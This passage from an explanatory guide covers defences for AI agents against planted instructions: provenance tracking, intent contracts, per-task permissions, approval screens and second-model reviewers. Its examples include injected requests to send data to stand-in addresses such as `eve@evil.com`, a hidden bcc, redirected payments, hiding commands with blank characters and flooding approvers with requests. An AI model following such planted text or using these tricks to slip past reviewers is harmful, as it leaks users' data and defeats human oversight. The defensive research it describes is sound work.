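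A successor called PRUDENTIA lets the user *endorse* a text, which relabels it as trusted. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an email with ten tasks. Endorsing the email takes one decision, whereas approving each resulting call would take ten. PRUDENTIA also tells the planner what the policies are, so the planner can avoid opening untrusted text unnecessarily. On AgentDojo, PRUDENTIA needed up to 1.9 times fewer human decisions than FIDES. The danger is that an endorsed email is trusted in full, including any planted line the user overlooked.

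### How a value loses its source inside the model

In an ordinary program, the runtime can follow a value from one variable to the next. *Sightline* (2026) points out that no code describes what happens inside a call to a language model. A program that tracks data therefore has to either stop tracking at the call or label the model's whole output as derived from everything in the prompt.

CaMeL and FIDES label everything the reader returns, which works because the reader receives only the text it needs. The same rule would leave an ordinary agent unable to act. Its single model holds both the employee's request and the supplier's page in its context, so every later argument would count as external, including the address the employee typed.

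Matching strings, as PACT does, avoids this but can miss a value that the model has rewritten. Suppose a planted line says to write to "the accounts team at flrm, spelled with an L, dot example". The model turns this into `accounts@flrm.example`, a string that appears in no email or web page, so the runtime finds no match and cannot determine where the address came from. If it treats unmatched addresses as trusted, it lets the attack through. It should therefore treat them as external, even though it will sometimes refuse an address that the model put together correctly from the employee's own words.

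Text can also influence a call without supplying any of its values. For example, a line planted in the report might lead the assistant to share the payroll file instead. Both files' IDs come from the drive's own list, so `file_id` would still pass the check in the table above.

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, a tool that checks an agent's logs for both kinds of influence. It compares meanings to find paraphrased text. To find influence on a choice, it removes the suspicious text and checks whether the agent would still have made the call. It also stores each memory's source with the memory, because a label kept only for one session would be lost by the next.

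The researchers tested NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios they wrote themselves, across 20 agent frameworks. It found 93.5 percent of the flows from outside text to sensitive calls, and 92.1 percent of its alarms were correct. Its F1 score, which combines those two measures, was 0.928, compared with 0.522 for FIDES. The test measures how well a system identifies flows, whereas FIDES is designed to restrict them, so its lower score doesn't measure how well it would block attacks. NeuroTaint works only after the agent has finished, so it can help an operator find out which invoice caused a bad payment, but it can't stop the payment.

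### What PACE found about coverage

It is still unclear how often a runtime loses track of a value in practice. PACE, a monitor that traces data from call to call, matches each argument against the values it has already seen. It also searches for disguised copies of protected data, such as text converted to base64 or hexadecimal. According to Li and colleagues, this search misses paraphrases, translations, short fragments and strings that the model recreates. Short, common values cause false matches with harmless text.

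PACE recorded 32,867 decisions in one set of tests. In 22,685 of those decisions, it found a risky path that it could cut. The counts leave out any path that PACE failed to record. The researchers say the counts aren't estimates of coverage, and they don't report what share of the real influences PACE detected.

They did measure what tracing paths costs. On 198 AgentDojo cases with a recent Qwen model, they turned the parts of PACE on and off:

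| Checks in use | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% |
| Path tracing alone | 0% | 13.6% |
| Checking effects against the user's request, alone | 0% | 64.6% |
| The complete system | 0% | 67.2% |

Path tracing alone stopped all the attacks but also most of the legitimate work. It has no exception for content arguments, so an untrusted email body can block a call just as an untrusted recipient can. PACE could remove one argument and let the rest of the call run, but only if the operator can guarantee that the model would have made the call without that argument. Operators can rarely guarantee this, so PACE usually blocks the whole call. The complete system recovers most of the lost work because its check against the user's request overrules many of those blocks.

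For the office assistant, the best way to preserve provenance is to avoid making the model copy important values. The runtime can give the model a short handle such as `contact_17` for an address in the directory and fill in the real address when the call runs. The operator can do the same for files and supplier accounts. The operator can also treat any address the model types out as external unless it exactly matches one in the employee's request. The source of the address is then certain, though the model may still pick the wrong person's handle.

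## Checking each call against the user's request

Suppose the employee writes, "Send the Q3 summary to my manager," and the assistant picks the legal team's address from the company directory. The directory is a trusted source that nobody has tampered with, and the recipient rules allow any colleague, so checking where the address came from won't stop the email from going to the wrong people. Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane (2027), in *Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, call such a value *trusted but unauthorized*. An outdated directory or an old email thread can supply one by accident, and a dishonest colleague can plant one in an internal document. To catch these values, the runtime has to compare them with what the user asked for.

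### IntentFlow's list of authorized values

Ameur and colleagues built IntentFlow, which runs between the model and its tools. It handles the request about the Q3 summary like this:

1. A language model turns the request into an *intent contract*, a structured list of what the user authorized. Here it contains one action, sending an email, and one recipient, "my manager".
2. IntentFlow looks up "my manager" in a directory of aliases, which somebody maintains by hand, and gets `manager@company.com`.
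3. When the agent proposes an email, IntentFlow puts each argument into a standard form and traces where its value came from.
4. It compares each authority-bearing argument with the contract. The value must match the contract or appear word for word in the request.
5. It reaches a decision for each argument (allow, rewrite, ask the user or block) and applies the strictest one to the whole call.

For a value $v$ in argument $a$, an intent contract $I$ and a provenance policy $P$, the rule is

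$$\text{Safe}(v,a) \iff \text{IntentAuthorizes}(v,a,I) \land \text{ProvenanceAllowed}(v,\text{role}(a),P)$$

The legal team's address meets the second condition but not the first. If the alias directory has no entry for a phrase, the phrase authorizes nothing, and IntentFlow either blocks the call or asks the user.

The word-for-word rule in step 4 is too loose. If the request contains `manager@company.com`, the prototype also accepts `ager@company.com`, because those characters appear in the request. An operator should compare whole addresses.

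### What IntentFlow blocked

The researchers tested IntentFlow on 200 simulated attacks, each of which changed one argument of a call:

| Argument the attack changed | Attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Recipient, attachment, meeting participant, file path or service endpoint | 134 | 0 |
| Database query | 34 | 0 |
| Content or payload field | 32 | 24 |

The 24 successful attacks changed email subjects, event descriptions and the text of files. These fields must accept whatever the model composes, so an attacker can still get a phishing message sent to the right person. IntentFlow allowed all 200 harmless versions of the same tasks and 46 of 50 harder ones.

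Checking only provenance let 101 of the 200 attacks succeed. Comparing only recipients, participants, paths and endpoints with the contract let 74 succeed. Most of the further improvement came from parsing database queries, and provenance checks blocked at most 16 more attacks. The comparison with the request therefore accounted for most of the blocked attacks, although it had the advantage of contracts that were correct by design.

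A separate set of 50 attacks used wrong values from trusted internal material. Checking provenance alone let all 50 through, while IntentFlow stopped them all and allowed all 50 harmless tasks. A simpler rule, loosely modeled on CaMeL, required each value to appear word for word in the request. It also stopped every attack but refused 16 of the harmless tasks, 13 because they used an alias for a service endpoint and 3 because they used an alias for a person.

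IntentFlow's lists of aliases solve that problem only if somebody keeps them complete. In a test of 30 harmless requests to service endpoints, IntentFlow allowed 14, because it couldn't match the others to its list of endpoints. Asking the user about unclear cases raised this to 28, assuming the user always answered correctly.

The results are better evidence about the comparison itself than about how IntentFlow would perform in an office. A program generated the main test from templates, and the researchers supplied the contracts, the argument roles and labels showing which documents contained planted text. A real system has to work out all three. When software inferred the roles of 150 arguments from six real connectors, it missed 25.9 percent of the authority-bearing ones. Each miss is dangerous because the argument then skips the strict check.

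Writing the contracts may be easier. Contracts written by GPT-4o-mini led to the same decisions on all 400 tasks in the main test, but the researchers caution that those tasks were too simple to test this well. They also ran 110 attacks against a live agent, still with correct contracts and labels. The agent proposed a corrupted call in 17 of them, and IntentFlow blocked all 17. Sixteen of those attacks put the instruction in one document and the false value in another.

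### Requests that leave details open

A contract is easy to write when the request contains every detail, but people use assistants partly to avoid spelling everything out. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *AutoDojo*, sorted AgentDojo's tasks by how much the user leaves to outside text:

| What the request determines | Example |
|---|---|
| The action and all its details | Change my address to the one given here |
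| The action, but not every detail | Pay the bill in a named file |
| Neither | Do everything on the to-do list at this web address |

A standard planted instruction succeeded against an undefended GPT-4o-mini in 87.5 percent of cases in the last group, compared with 63.9 and 43.3 percent in the other two. Filters that search for suspicious text seemed to help until the researchers adapted the attacks to them, which raised the success rate in the last group to between 46 and 54 percent against three of these filters. If the user has asked the agent to do whatever a list contains, an attack can look like another item.

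Three systems that restrict tool calls did much better, with at most 11 percent of attacks succeeding in any group. But two of them allow only reading on many of the open-ended tasks, which presumably also blocks some of the work the user wanted.

AgentDojo's results understate this drawback. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) reports that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan along the way, so a defense can score well by holding the agent to its first plan. *AgentDyn*'s own test set has 60 tasks that average about seven steps, and all of them require replanning. Agents whose defenses relied on an initial plan completed far fewer of these tasks.

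### How SARA separates details from new authority

SARA, the mechanism from *When Tool Outputs Become Commands*, lets tool results fill in the details of an authorized task but not add to the task. It keeps three records:

- a contract that lists the effects the user authorized, their scope and any values she gave, but not the sequence of tool calls
- the actions that outside text has proposed, with their arguments
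- the calls that SARA allowed and that succeeded, with their results

The second record comes from the *Action Probe*, a language model that examines each tool result without seeing the user's request. It looks for text that would prompt a tool call by itself, and records the tool and the values. It doesn't judge whether the text is malicious. For example, the probe records an email address as a proposed recipient if it appears in the sentence "forward the report to this address", but treats the same address in a signature as ordinary data.

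Once the probe has found such text, every later call with side effects gets a full review until the task ends. A call $c$ must pass three tests:

$$\text{Auth}(c) = G(c) \land C(c) \land A(c)$$

$G$ requires the operation and its target to be within the contract. $C$ requires the objects the call depends on to come from earlier successful calls that served the task. $A$ requires each argument to be supported by the user's request, one of those earlier calls or a harmless default.

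Suppose the employee typed Alice's address when asking for the quarterly report. The email to Alice passes because the request supports the recipient and the search result supports the path. If the search result also contains an instruction to send a copy to `copy@attacker.test`, the copy fails because nothing else supports its recipient.

An attacker could first get the assistant to search its contacts for `copy@attacker.test`, so that the address also appears in the result of a successful call. SARA therefore lets only the user's request authorize a value that outside text first proposed, even if the value turns up again later. Removing this rule raised the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 0.06 to 0.65 percent.

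These are SARA's main results. Each cell gives the figure without SARA and then with it:

| Model and test set | Successful attacks | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini, AgentDojo | 15.79% → 0.06% | 72.5% → 66.7% | 56.0% → 63.4% |
| GPT-4o-mini, AgentDyn | 16.07% → 0.17% | 65.0% → 56.0% | 54.6% → 54.9% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite, AgentDojo | 33.28% → 0.62% | 87.7% → 81.2% | 57.4% → 77.3% |
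| Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite, AgentDyn | 30.91% → 0.63% | 79.0% → 67.1% | 58.8% → 64.9% |

SARA lowered task completion by 6 to 12 percentage points when there was no attack. CaMeL had even lower attack rates than SARA in three of the four settings, but it lowered task completion by 16 to 40 points. CaMeL completed 25 and 49 percent of the AgentDyn tasks in these tests, far more than in the tests of PACE, so its results clearly depend heavily on the models and the setup.

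Removing SARA's record of successful calls did not make attacks more successful, but it lowered task completion under attack by 10 points on AgentDojo and 13 on AgentDyn, because the agent could no longer rely on file names and IDs it had looked up. Without the test on arguments, 2.5 to 2.7 percent of attacks succeeded. These attacks kept to the general task but changed a detail such as the recipient.

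SARA roughly doubles the amount of text the models have to process, and its judgments come from language models, which can be wrong. It also wouldn't catch the mistake with the legal team's address, because the full review starts only when outside text includes a proposed action, and an ordinary directory listing doesn't include one.

### ToolFence and the redirected bill payment

A *within-tool attack* uses a tool that the user's task needs but changes an authority-bearing argument, so a list of permitted tools can't stop it. To count these attacks in AgentDojo, Li and colleagues, who built ToolFence, compared the calls required by each user task with those required by the attack paired with it. Of 629 pairs, 524 attacks needed an extra tool, 85 needed only tools that the task already used, and 20 couldn't be classified. About half of the within-tool attacks were in banking, where the agent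 often has a good reason to make a payment.

ToolFence converts the user's request into permissions for that task alone. Each permission specifies a tool, its effect, the source of every sensitive argument, the stage of the task, and a *budget*, the number of times the agent may use it. A language model writes the permissions before the agent reads any outside text, and ordinary code enforces them.

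In the researchers' example, a user asks the agent to pay $100 to the recipient named in a bill. The bill names BillPay, but another tool result contains an instruction to pay Mallory:

1. ToolFence creates a permission for one payment of $100 to the recipient named in that bill.
2. The agent opens the bill, and ToolFence records the name BillPay.
3. The planted instruction misleads the agent, which proposes `send_money("Mallory", 100)`. The tool and the amount are correct, but Mallory isn't the recipient in the bill, so ToolFence refuses the call.
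4. The agent learns of the refusal and proposes `send_money("BillPay", 100)`. ToolFence reserves the permission's only use and makes the payment.
5. If the agent proposes the same payment again, ToolFence refuses because the budget is used up.

If the connection fails during the payment, ToolFence keeps the permission's use reserved until the outcome is known, so a retry can't pay BillPay twice. But ToolFence can't verify that the bill is genuine. If the attacker had written the bill, Mallory would have been the correct recipient under this permission. The office assistant's gateway would still stop that payment unless Mallory were an approved supplier.

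If the first set of permissions leaves out a necessary step, such as searching a drive for an attachment, ToolFence asks a separate language model to review the missing permission. This reviewer receives the user's request and a description of the permission, for example "a payment whose recipient comes from the user's request", but no values and no text from tool results. It is instructed to refuse when unsure, and to refuse any permission that would let the agent make up a sensitive value. If the reviewer approves the permission, the agent proposes the call again and the code checks the actual values.

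On AgentDojo with Qwen3-max, ToolFence reduced the attack success rate from 21.2 percent to zero, while the completion rate for ordinary tasks fell from 66.3 to 64.3 percent. ToolFence slowed the agent far less than CaMeL did.

The researchers removed parts of the system in a different test, which used Llama 3.3 and also included planted memories. Without the argument checks, the attack success rate rose from 5.1 to 24.0 percent. Without the reviewer, security stayed about the same, but the agent completed only 35.8 percent of its tasks under attack, compared with 44.3 percent with the full system and 40.1 percent with no defense.

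Another experiment added the limits one at a time and measured how many unauthorized banking calls still got through:

| Limits in the permission | Unauthorized calls accepted |
|---|---|
| Tool only | 89.3% |
| Tool and source of each argument | 84.5% |
| Tool, source and stage of the task | 45.2% |
| Tool, source, stage and budget | 6.0% |

Stage and budget had large effects partly because the researchers had added test calls that were made at the wrong stage or exceeded the budget. The last 6 percent, five calls, came from a single task in which the user's own request gave the attacker's account number as a new landlord's, and comparing a call with the request can't catch a false value that the user typed.

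### Progent's written policies

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) expresses a task's permissions as rules that allow or forbid a tool call depending on its arguments. It refuses any call that no rule allows. A language model writes rules for each task and proposes changes as the agent learns more, but the operator's fixed rules take priority.

Progent treats a change that removes permissions differently from one that adds them. Let $A(P)$ be the set of calls that policy $P$ allows. A new policy $P'$ takes effect automatically only if

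$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

A solver, a program that can prove statements about all possible argument values, checks this condition. If the new policy would allow even one additional call, somebody has to approve it.

The paper's example is a user who asks an agent to carry out the tasks in a certain email:

1. The first policy allows only a search for that email.
2. The email asks for a summary of the user's recent messages, posted to their Slack account. The model proposes rules for reading email, looking up the account and posting to Slack. These add permissions, so they need approval.
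3. The lookup returns the user's Slack name, and the model restricts posting to that name. This removes permissions and takes effect immediately.
4. One of the recent messages contains an instruction to forward the inbox to `eve@evil.com`. If this fools the model into proposing a rule for sending email, the solver detects the added permission, and the rule waits for approval.

With GPT-4o on AgentDojo, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9 to 1.0 percent. The researchers had it approve every added permission automatically, to imitate a careless user. The first policy alone, which the model wrote before seeing any outside text, reduced the rate to 2.5 percent. When a person reviewed the first policy and every addition, no attack succeeded. Only 6 percent of policy changes added permissions, so the reviewer would have had little to review.

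If an operator automatically approves every addition, the solver's check is irrelevant, because a model that falls for planted text can widen its own policy. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticizes Progent for this dependence on the model, and adds that people make mistakes when they write policies by hand. The criticism appears to concern a version without the solver, but it still applies with the solver if approval is automatic.

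Other researchers also found Progent useful, but their results were weaker. In tests by Ma and colleagues, 7.7 percent of adapted attacks succeeded against it with GPT-4o-mini, and it lowered task completion by up to 7 percentage points. Li and colleagues found that it sharply reduced task completion on AgentDyn, because accurate rules are hard to write for an agent with many tools.

A policy must also be precise to catch wrong values from trusted sources. Ameur and colleagues tested a simplified imitation of Progent that approved recipients by domain, and 39 of their 50 attacks got through. A real Progent policy could allow only the manager's address, but the model writing it would first need a reliable way to identify the manager.

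### Permissions for one request to the office assistant

The office assistant's operator can combine these ideas. When the employee writes, "pay the invoice in my contracts folder and mail the receipt to my manager," the runtime creates these permissions:

| Tool | Budget | What the arguments must match |
|---|---|---|
| `read_file` | No limit | The contracts folder and the files in it |
| `get_supplier` | One call | The supplier named on the invoice |
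| `send_payment` | One call | The account in that supplier's record, and the amount and number on the invoice |
| `send_email` | One call | The manager's address, and the receipt that `send_payment` returned |

The manager's address should come from a lookup that returns only the employee's manager. If the permission accepted any address from the full directory, the legal team's address would pass. For common requests like this one, the operator can write the permissions as a template, so the model only has to choose the template and fill in the folder.

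An invoice could still redirect the payment to a different approved supplier, because the employee never said whom she wanted to pay. If she had written "pay Norwood's invoice", the runtime could have fixed the recipient from the start. The operator can also prevent the redirection without her help if the accounting system records the supplier for each unpaid invoice. The gateway then refuses a payment whose recipient and invoice number don't match.

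### When an outside instruction is legitimate

Suppose the operator gives the assistant a browser, and the employee asks it to download a statement from a supplier's website. The site emails her a one-time code and displays an instruction to enter it. The instruction comes from outside the company, but the assistant has to follow it to finish the job. The AgentDyn tasks all include a helpful instruction of this kind. When Li and colleagues tested two filters that remove instructions from outside text, the agents completed almost none of these tasks.

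Login codes are also valuable to thieves, so trusting every message about a code would be dangerous. Li and colleagues use a login code as one of ToolFence's motivating cases. ToolFence takes its authority from the user's request and treats the website's text only as information. The employee's request requires logging in, so after starting the login, the assistant may read one new message from that site and enter the code there once. These permissions don't allow it to email the code to anyone or enter it elsewhere. ToolFence can also tie a code to a particular transaction. In one example, a code issued for order O99 can't confirm order O17.

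The operator can make this safer with a tool that finds the code and enters it without showing it to the model. The assistant then doesn't need general access to login messages.

An instruction that the request doesn't clearly cover is harder to judge. The supplier's website might ask the assistant to confirm the company's bank details before letting it download the statement. Some honest websites do this, but a phishing page would too. The reviewer has to decide whether the step is necessary based on evidence that an attacker could have prepared.

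AgentLAB, a test set of long attacks, spreads planted text across search results, emails, calendar entries and files, so that a harmful action looks like a normal part of the work. ToolFence cut the success rate of these attacks from 76.3 to 29.4 percent against Qwen3-max and from 82.1 to 38.3 percent against Llama 3.3. The resulting rates were the lowest of any defense in the comparison, but they are far too high for an agent that can make payments. According to Li and colleagues, one cause is that the reviewer can grant overly broad permissions when an attacker makes a step look necessary. The office assistant's reviewer should therefore approve an extra step only if it just reads from folders and accounts already open to the task. If an extra step would disclose data, change a record or move money, the runtime should ask the employee.

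## Asking a person to approve a call

The rules so far leave some decisions to the employee, such as a payment above 500 or a reply to an unknown address on a supplier's thread. Asking her helps only if the screen shows enough for her to tell a bad call from a good one and the questions are rare enough that she still reads them.

### Which calls go to a person

*A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) describes an arrangement in which rules that forbid a call have absolute priority, rules that allow low-risk calls come next, and a person decides on the remaining calls. If company policy forbids a call, the system should never ask an employee to approve it, because the employee might say yes.

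To decide which other calls need a person's approval, the operator can consider whether the effect can be undone, whether it reaches people outside the company, and whether the automatic checks reached a decision. If the effect is permanent and reaches people outside the company, the runtime should ask for approval unless an exact rule covers the values in the call. If the checks can't decide, it should ask regardless of the effect.

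| Proposed call | Can she undo it? | Does it leave the company? | Did the checks decide? | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Email the quarterly report to Alice | No | No | Yes, Alice is in the directory | Runs |
| Pay an approved supplier 98.70 | Rarely | Yes | Yes, the account, amount and invoice match | Runs |
| Pay an approved supplier 3,200 | Rarely | Yes | No, the amount is above the automatic limit | Employee decides |
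| Email a contract to `dana@audit.example` | No | Yes | No, she typed the address but it is on no list | Employee decides |
| Share the contracts folder with a supplier | Partly | Yes | Yes, a rule forbids it | Refused |

The runtime has to apply these tests, because models are unreliable at knowing when to ask. In one experiment from *DelegationBench* (2026), models received a standing policy and a task and could either act or ask. They were right in 89.6 percent of cases when they had permission, but only 64.8 percent when permission was missing. The second figure rose to 79.6 percent when questions that asked for both permission and a missing fact were counted as correct. Instructing an agent to ask first doesn't replace the runtime's tests either. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, describes a safety researcher who told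 her agent to confirm before acting. It began deleting her email anyway and didn't stop when she told it to.

### What the approver needs to see

| Family | What the screen must show | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Message | Every recipient, every attachment and the full text | To `dana@audit.example`, no copies, `contract.pdf`, followed by the whole email |
| File | The real location after following links, and the exact change | Six named files move from "Old drafts" to the trash |
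| Service | The account or record the service will use, the amount, and the values before and after | Norwood's phone number changes from 555-0142 to 555-0199 |

It is hard to tell from a command how it will affect files. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), which analyzes reports of agents damaging files, describes an agent that removed the whole set of programming tools while trying to fix a missing header. In nearly a fifth of the reports that showed whether the user noticed the damage, the user noticed late or never.

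Sometimes a call looks fine and the problem lies in earlier steps. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who wants the agent to send an auditor only summary totals. An instruction planted in a vendor's note leads the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name are as expected, so the approver can catch the mistake only if the screen also shows what the file contains or where its contents came from.

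The researchers tested four screens on 80 volunteers, 20 for each screen. Every volunteer judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe.

| What the screen showed | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The arguments, the user's original restriction and a log of every step | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
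| The same facts, with a statement linking the relevant steps | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from showing more facts. The advantage of the linked version over the plain log could be due to chance. People could recognize some unsafe requests from the call alone, for example because the recipient was prohibited, but they still approved 10 of 40 of these with the log and 7 of 40 with the linked version. An employee would probably do worse, since the volunteers had no other job to finish and half the requests were unsafe.

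### Why the runtime has to write the screen

Many approval prompts show the agent's own description of the call. If planted text has misled the agent, the description may be wrong too. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) demonstrates this with a user who asks an agent to send a report to his boss. The agent adds a `bcc` to an attacker's address and leaves that recipient out of an otherwise accurate description of the email. All 15 current language models tested as approvers allowed the call when shown the description, but refused it when shown a card that software had built from the call's arguments.

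Across 23 attacks, the models caught 30 percent when shown the description and 98 percent when shown the card. They also refused 16 percent of harmless requests when shown the card, but none when shown the description. In most of those refusals, the models objected to placeholder text that stood in for real messages. Without these refusals, the rate would have been about 2 percent. The study had no human approvers, so it shows what information the description leaves out, but not how often people would notice it on the card.

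Adding the agent's explanation to the card can undo the benefit. In a simulation of an approver who always believes the agent, 54 percent of attacks succeeded when the card included the explanation, the same as with the description alone. Without the explanation, the card reduced this to 5 percent. The explanation didn't affect the language models, but operators should leave it out unless they are sure people will ignore it.

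The approval prompt also needs to display the call's arguments carefully, because an attacker may control some of them. A long run of blank characters can push the harmful part of a command off the screen, and an argument named "Verified by client" can look like a label from the system. Kodathala and colleagues therefore make invisible characters visible, list every recipient in the prompt's title and put argument names chosen by the agent in a separate section.

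The answer also has to arrive through a channel that the agent can't write to and a stranger can't use. In one case from the paper, an agent asked for confirmation before a destructive reset and accepted it from the requester, who wasn't the owner. A button in the company's own interface, behind the employee's login, avoids this.

### Tying an approval to one exact call

The agent may change a call after the employee has approved it. To prevent this, the runtime can compute a *hash*, a short fingerprint of the call that changes when any argument changes. For a tool $\tau$ with arguments $\theta$,

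$$h = \text{SHA-256}(\text{canonical}(\tau, \theta))$$

SHA-256 is a standard hash function. The canonical form fixes details such as the order of the arguments, so that the same call always has the same hash. The approval then works like this:

1. The runtime stores the call in canonical form and computes $h$.
2. It builds the screen from the stored call.
3. If the employee approves, it records her decision with $h$, an expiry time and an ID that works only once.
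4. Just before execution, it hashes the call that is about to run. If the result isn't $h$, it refuses the call.
5. It marks the approval as used.

Suppose she approves the email to Dana, and the agent then resubmits it with a `bcc`. The hash no longer matches, so her approval is void. IntentFlow, by Ameur and colleagues, makes the same comparison, and the gateway by Kodathala and colleagues goes further by running only the stored call. The hash should also cover the contents of any attachment, because if it covers only the file's ID, somebody can edit the file between the approval and the sending without voiding her approval.

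Kodathala and colleagues also examined how ten agent runtimes handle approvals. They could measure this binding in eight approval mechanisms: three passed, one passed partly and four failed. In LangGraph and Agno, two widely used frameworks, anyone able to resume a paused run could replace the arguments and have the new call executed. Five mechanisms ran an approved call a second time if somebody restored the run to an earlier state, which would make a payment go through twice. An operator should test for both problems before relying on a framework's approval mechanism.

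### How often people catch a bad call

Claude Code's users approve 97 percent of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). An earlier Anthropic post, *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, reported 93 percent. Most commands are harmless, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people have stopped reading the prompts. Users also reject 39 percent of the plans that Claude presents for approval, so they do push back when a question seems worth their time.

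Anthropic also tested this directly, through a research vendor that gave 1,053 paid testers coding work in a test environment. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6 percent, refused it. Testers blocked about 17 percent of dangerous commands early in a session, but about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts. The low overall rate may exaggerate the problem, because Anthropic sells the automated alternative and the testers had no projects of their own to lose, but these factors don't explain the decline during a session as easily.

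An attacker can exploit an approver's fatigue by making the agent ask for approval repeatedly. Kodathala and colleagues could test seven mechanisms for this weakness, and none limited the number of requests. In five frameworks, one model response could create 20 pending approvals. Their own gateway allows one pending request per session and locks the agent out after three refusals. With these limits, a simulated approver who reads only the main fields of each request and sometimes misses a wrong value still let the attack through 45 to 60 percent of the time, compared with every time without them.

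### Prompts per day

The number of prompts is the number of calls multiplied by the share that needs review. For an agent that makes 1,000 calls a day, the median times from the study by Hossain and colleagues give a rough idea of the work involved:

| Share of calls sent to a person | Prompts a day | Time at 16.3 seconds each | Time at 33.2 seconds each |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 10 | 3 minutes | 6 minutes |
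| 10% | 100 | 27 minutes | 55 minutes |

The employee can manage ten prompts a day. Reading a hundred properly would take her most of an hour, so she probably wouldn't, and by the second fifty she would be at the point where Anthropic's testers caught about one dangerous command in twenty. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) describes a model in which the reviewer tires, so a guard that requests approval for 500 actions a day can be less safe than one that requests it for five, because routine requests use up the attention needed for a dangerous one.

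LivePI's defense sent about 1 percent of calls to a person, but an assistant that works in an inbox will start with a higher rate. The operator can lower it by finding the kinds of calls the employee always approves and allowing them without a prompt. If half the prompts are about messages to the same outside accountant, adding that address to the list of permitted recipients removes those prompts and leaves the unusual ones.

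### How "always allow" becomes a standing rule

Many prompts include an "always allow" button, which applies the employee's decision about one call to later calls she hasn't seen. If she clicks it on the email to Dana, her approval may cover only emails to that address, or every email the assistant sends.

Users tend to set broad rules. Anthropic found that 62 percent of Claude Code users had either turned on the mode that skips permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands. Many had written rules such as `python:*`, which allows any Python program and therefore nearly anything a shell can do. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025), 95.1 percent of participants told an agent to "always share" at least one kind of data, though many reconsidered when the agent made mistakes.

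A standing permission is safer when it lets as little as possible change between calls. Kodathala and colleagues let the user allow changes only to the amount, up to a cap, and to text, up to a set length. The recipient, account, path and web address must stay the same. The permission also expires, has a maximum number of uses and covers one tool in one session. It is still risky if the approver is inattentive. In their simulation of a person who approves 30 percent of requests without reading them, offering this option raised the success rate of one attack from 30 to 70 percent, because a careless approval also covered later calls.

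People who set rules in advance can still let through actions they didn't request. Yan had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise a simulated agent that took 18 actions, 7 of them unrequested. Some decided whether to approve each action, some relied on a model's review, and some first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for four categories such as spending money. About 60 percent of the unrequested actions went through when people set rules, compared with about 40 percent when they decided on each action and 46 percent with model review.

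The rules reduced the average number of prompts from 18.0 to 10.9. But people chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules, which postponed the decision, and they approved 133 of the 148 unrequested actions that went through. The experiment compared whole designs, so it can't show why this group approved so many. For the office assistant, the operator should write the standing rules from the log of past calls and reserve "ask" for cases that vary.

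### Review by a second model

Coding agents increasingly send these approval requests to another model. Claude Code's *auto mode* became the default for new sessions on several plans in August 2026, and OpenAI's Codex has a similar mode called Auto-review. In the version Anthropic first described, auto mode lets the agent read files and edit the project folder without review. For other calls, the reviewing model first gives a quick yes-or-no answer, erring toward blocking. If it flags a call, it reconsiders with step-by-step reasoning. After 3 blocks in a row or 20 in a session, a person takes over.

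Anthropic has published several error rates, for different versions and kinds of danger:

| Test | Dangerous calls the reviewer missed |
|---|---|
| 52 real calls in which Claude exceeded the user's request | 17% |
| 1,000 generated attempts to leak data | 5.7% |
| The commands shown to the 1,053 testers | 11% |
| Attacks by the safety company Apollo Research, after Anthropic's fixes | 7% |

The first version wrongly blocked 0.4 percent of 10,000 ordinary calls. At that rate, it would wrongly block 4 calls a day for the agent in the example above. The agent can usually find another way to continue.

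Text that fools the agent could also fool the reviewer, so Anthropic shows its reviewer the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the results of those calls or the agent's explanations. If a file contains an instruction to post passwords to a website and the agent follows it, the reviewer sees only the attempt to post them, which the user never requested. ToolFence's reviewer also doesn't see text from tool results. An attacker's words can still reach the reviewer in a tool call's arguments, for example when the agent copies them into an email.

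Withholding the results from the reviewer also hides where a value came from. An account number from a forged invoice looks the same as a real one, so the office assistant's gateway would still have to check it against the supplier's record. The reviewer can also misjudge consent. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but treated something the user had said as permission. A request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change), for example, doesn't authorize overwriting the project's history.

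Vague requests make this worse. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports an outside test of 128 deliberately ambiguous scenarios, in which auto mode missed 81 percent of the dangerous actions. It missed many of them because edits inside the project folder skipped the reviewer. Since the scenarios were chosen to be ambiguous, 81 percent isn't an everyday error rate.

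Tests with planted instructions went better. In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, none of 720 attacks succeeded against recent Claude models in auto mode. Only 0.09 percent succeeded with auto mode off, so the reviewer accounts for little of this result. Auto-review made a larger difference for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, cutting the share of attacks that succeeded from 19.03 to 5.83 percent.

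On this evidence, a second model judges routine calls better than a tired person does. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes themselves. The office assistant's operator could let a model decide on replies to known suppliers and ask the employee to approve only calls that involve large payments or new outside recipients. She would also have fewer prompts to read.

### Confirmation requests in MCP

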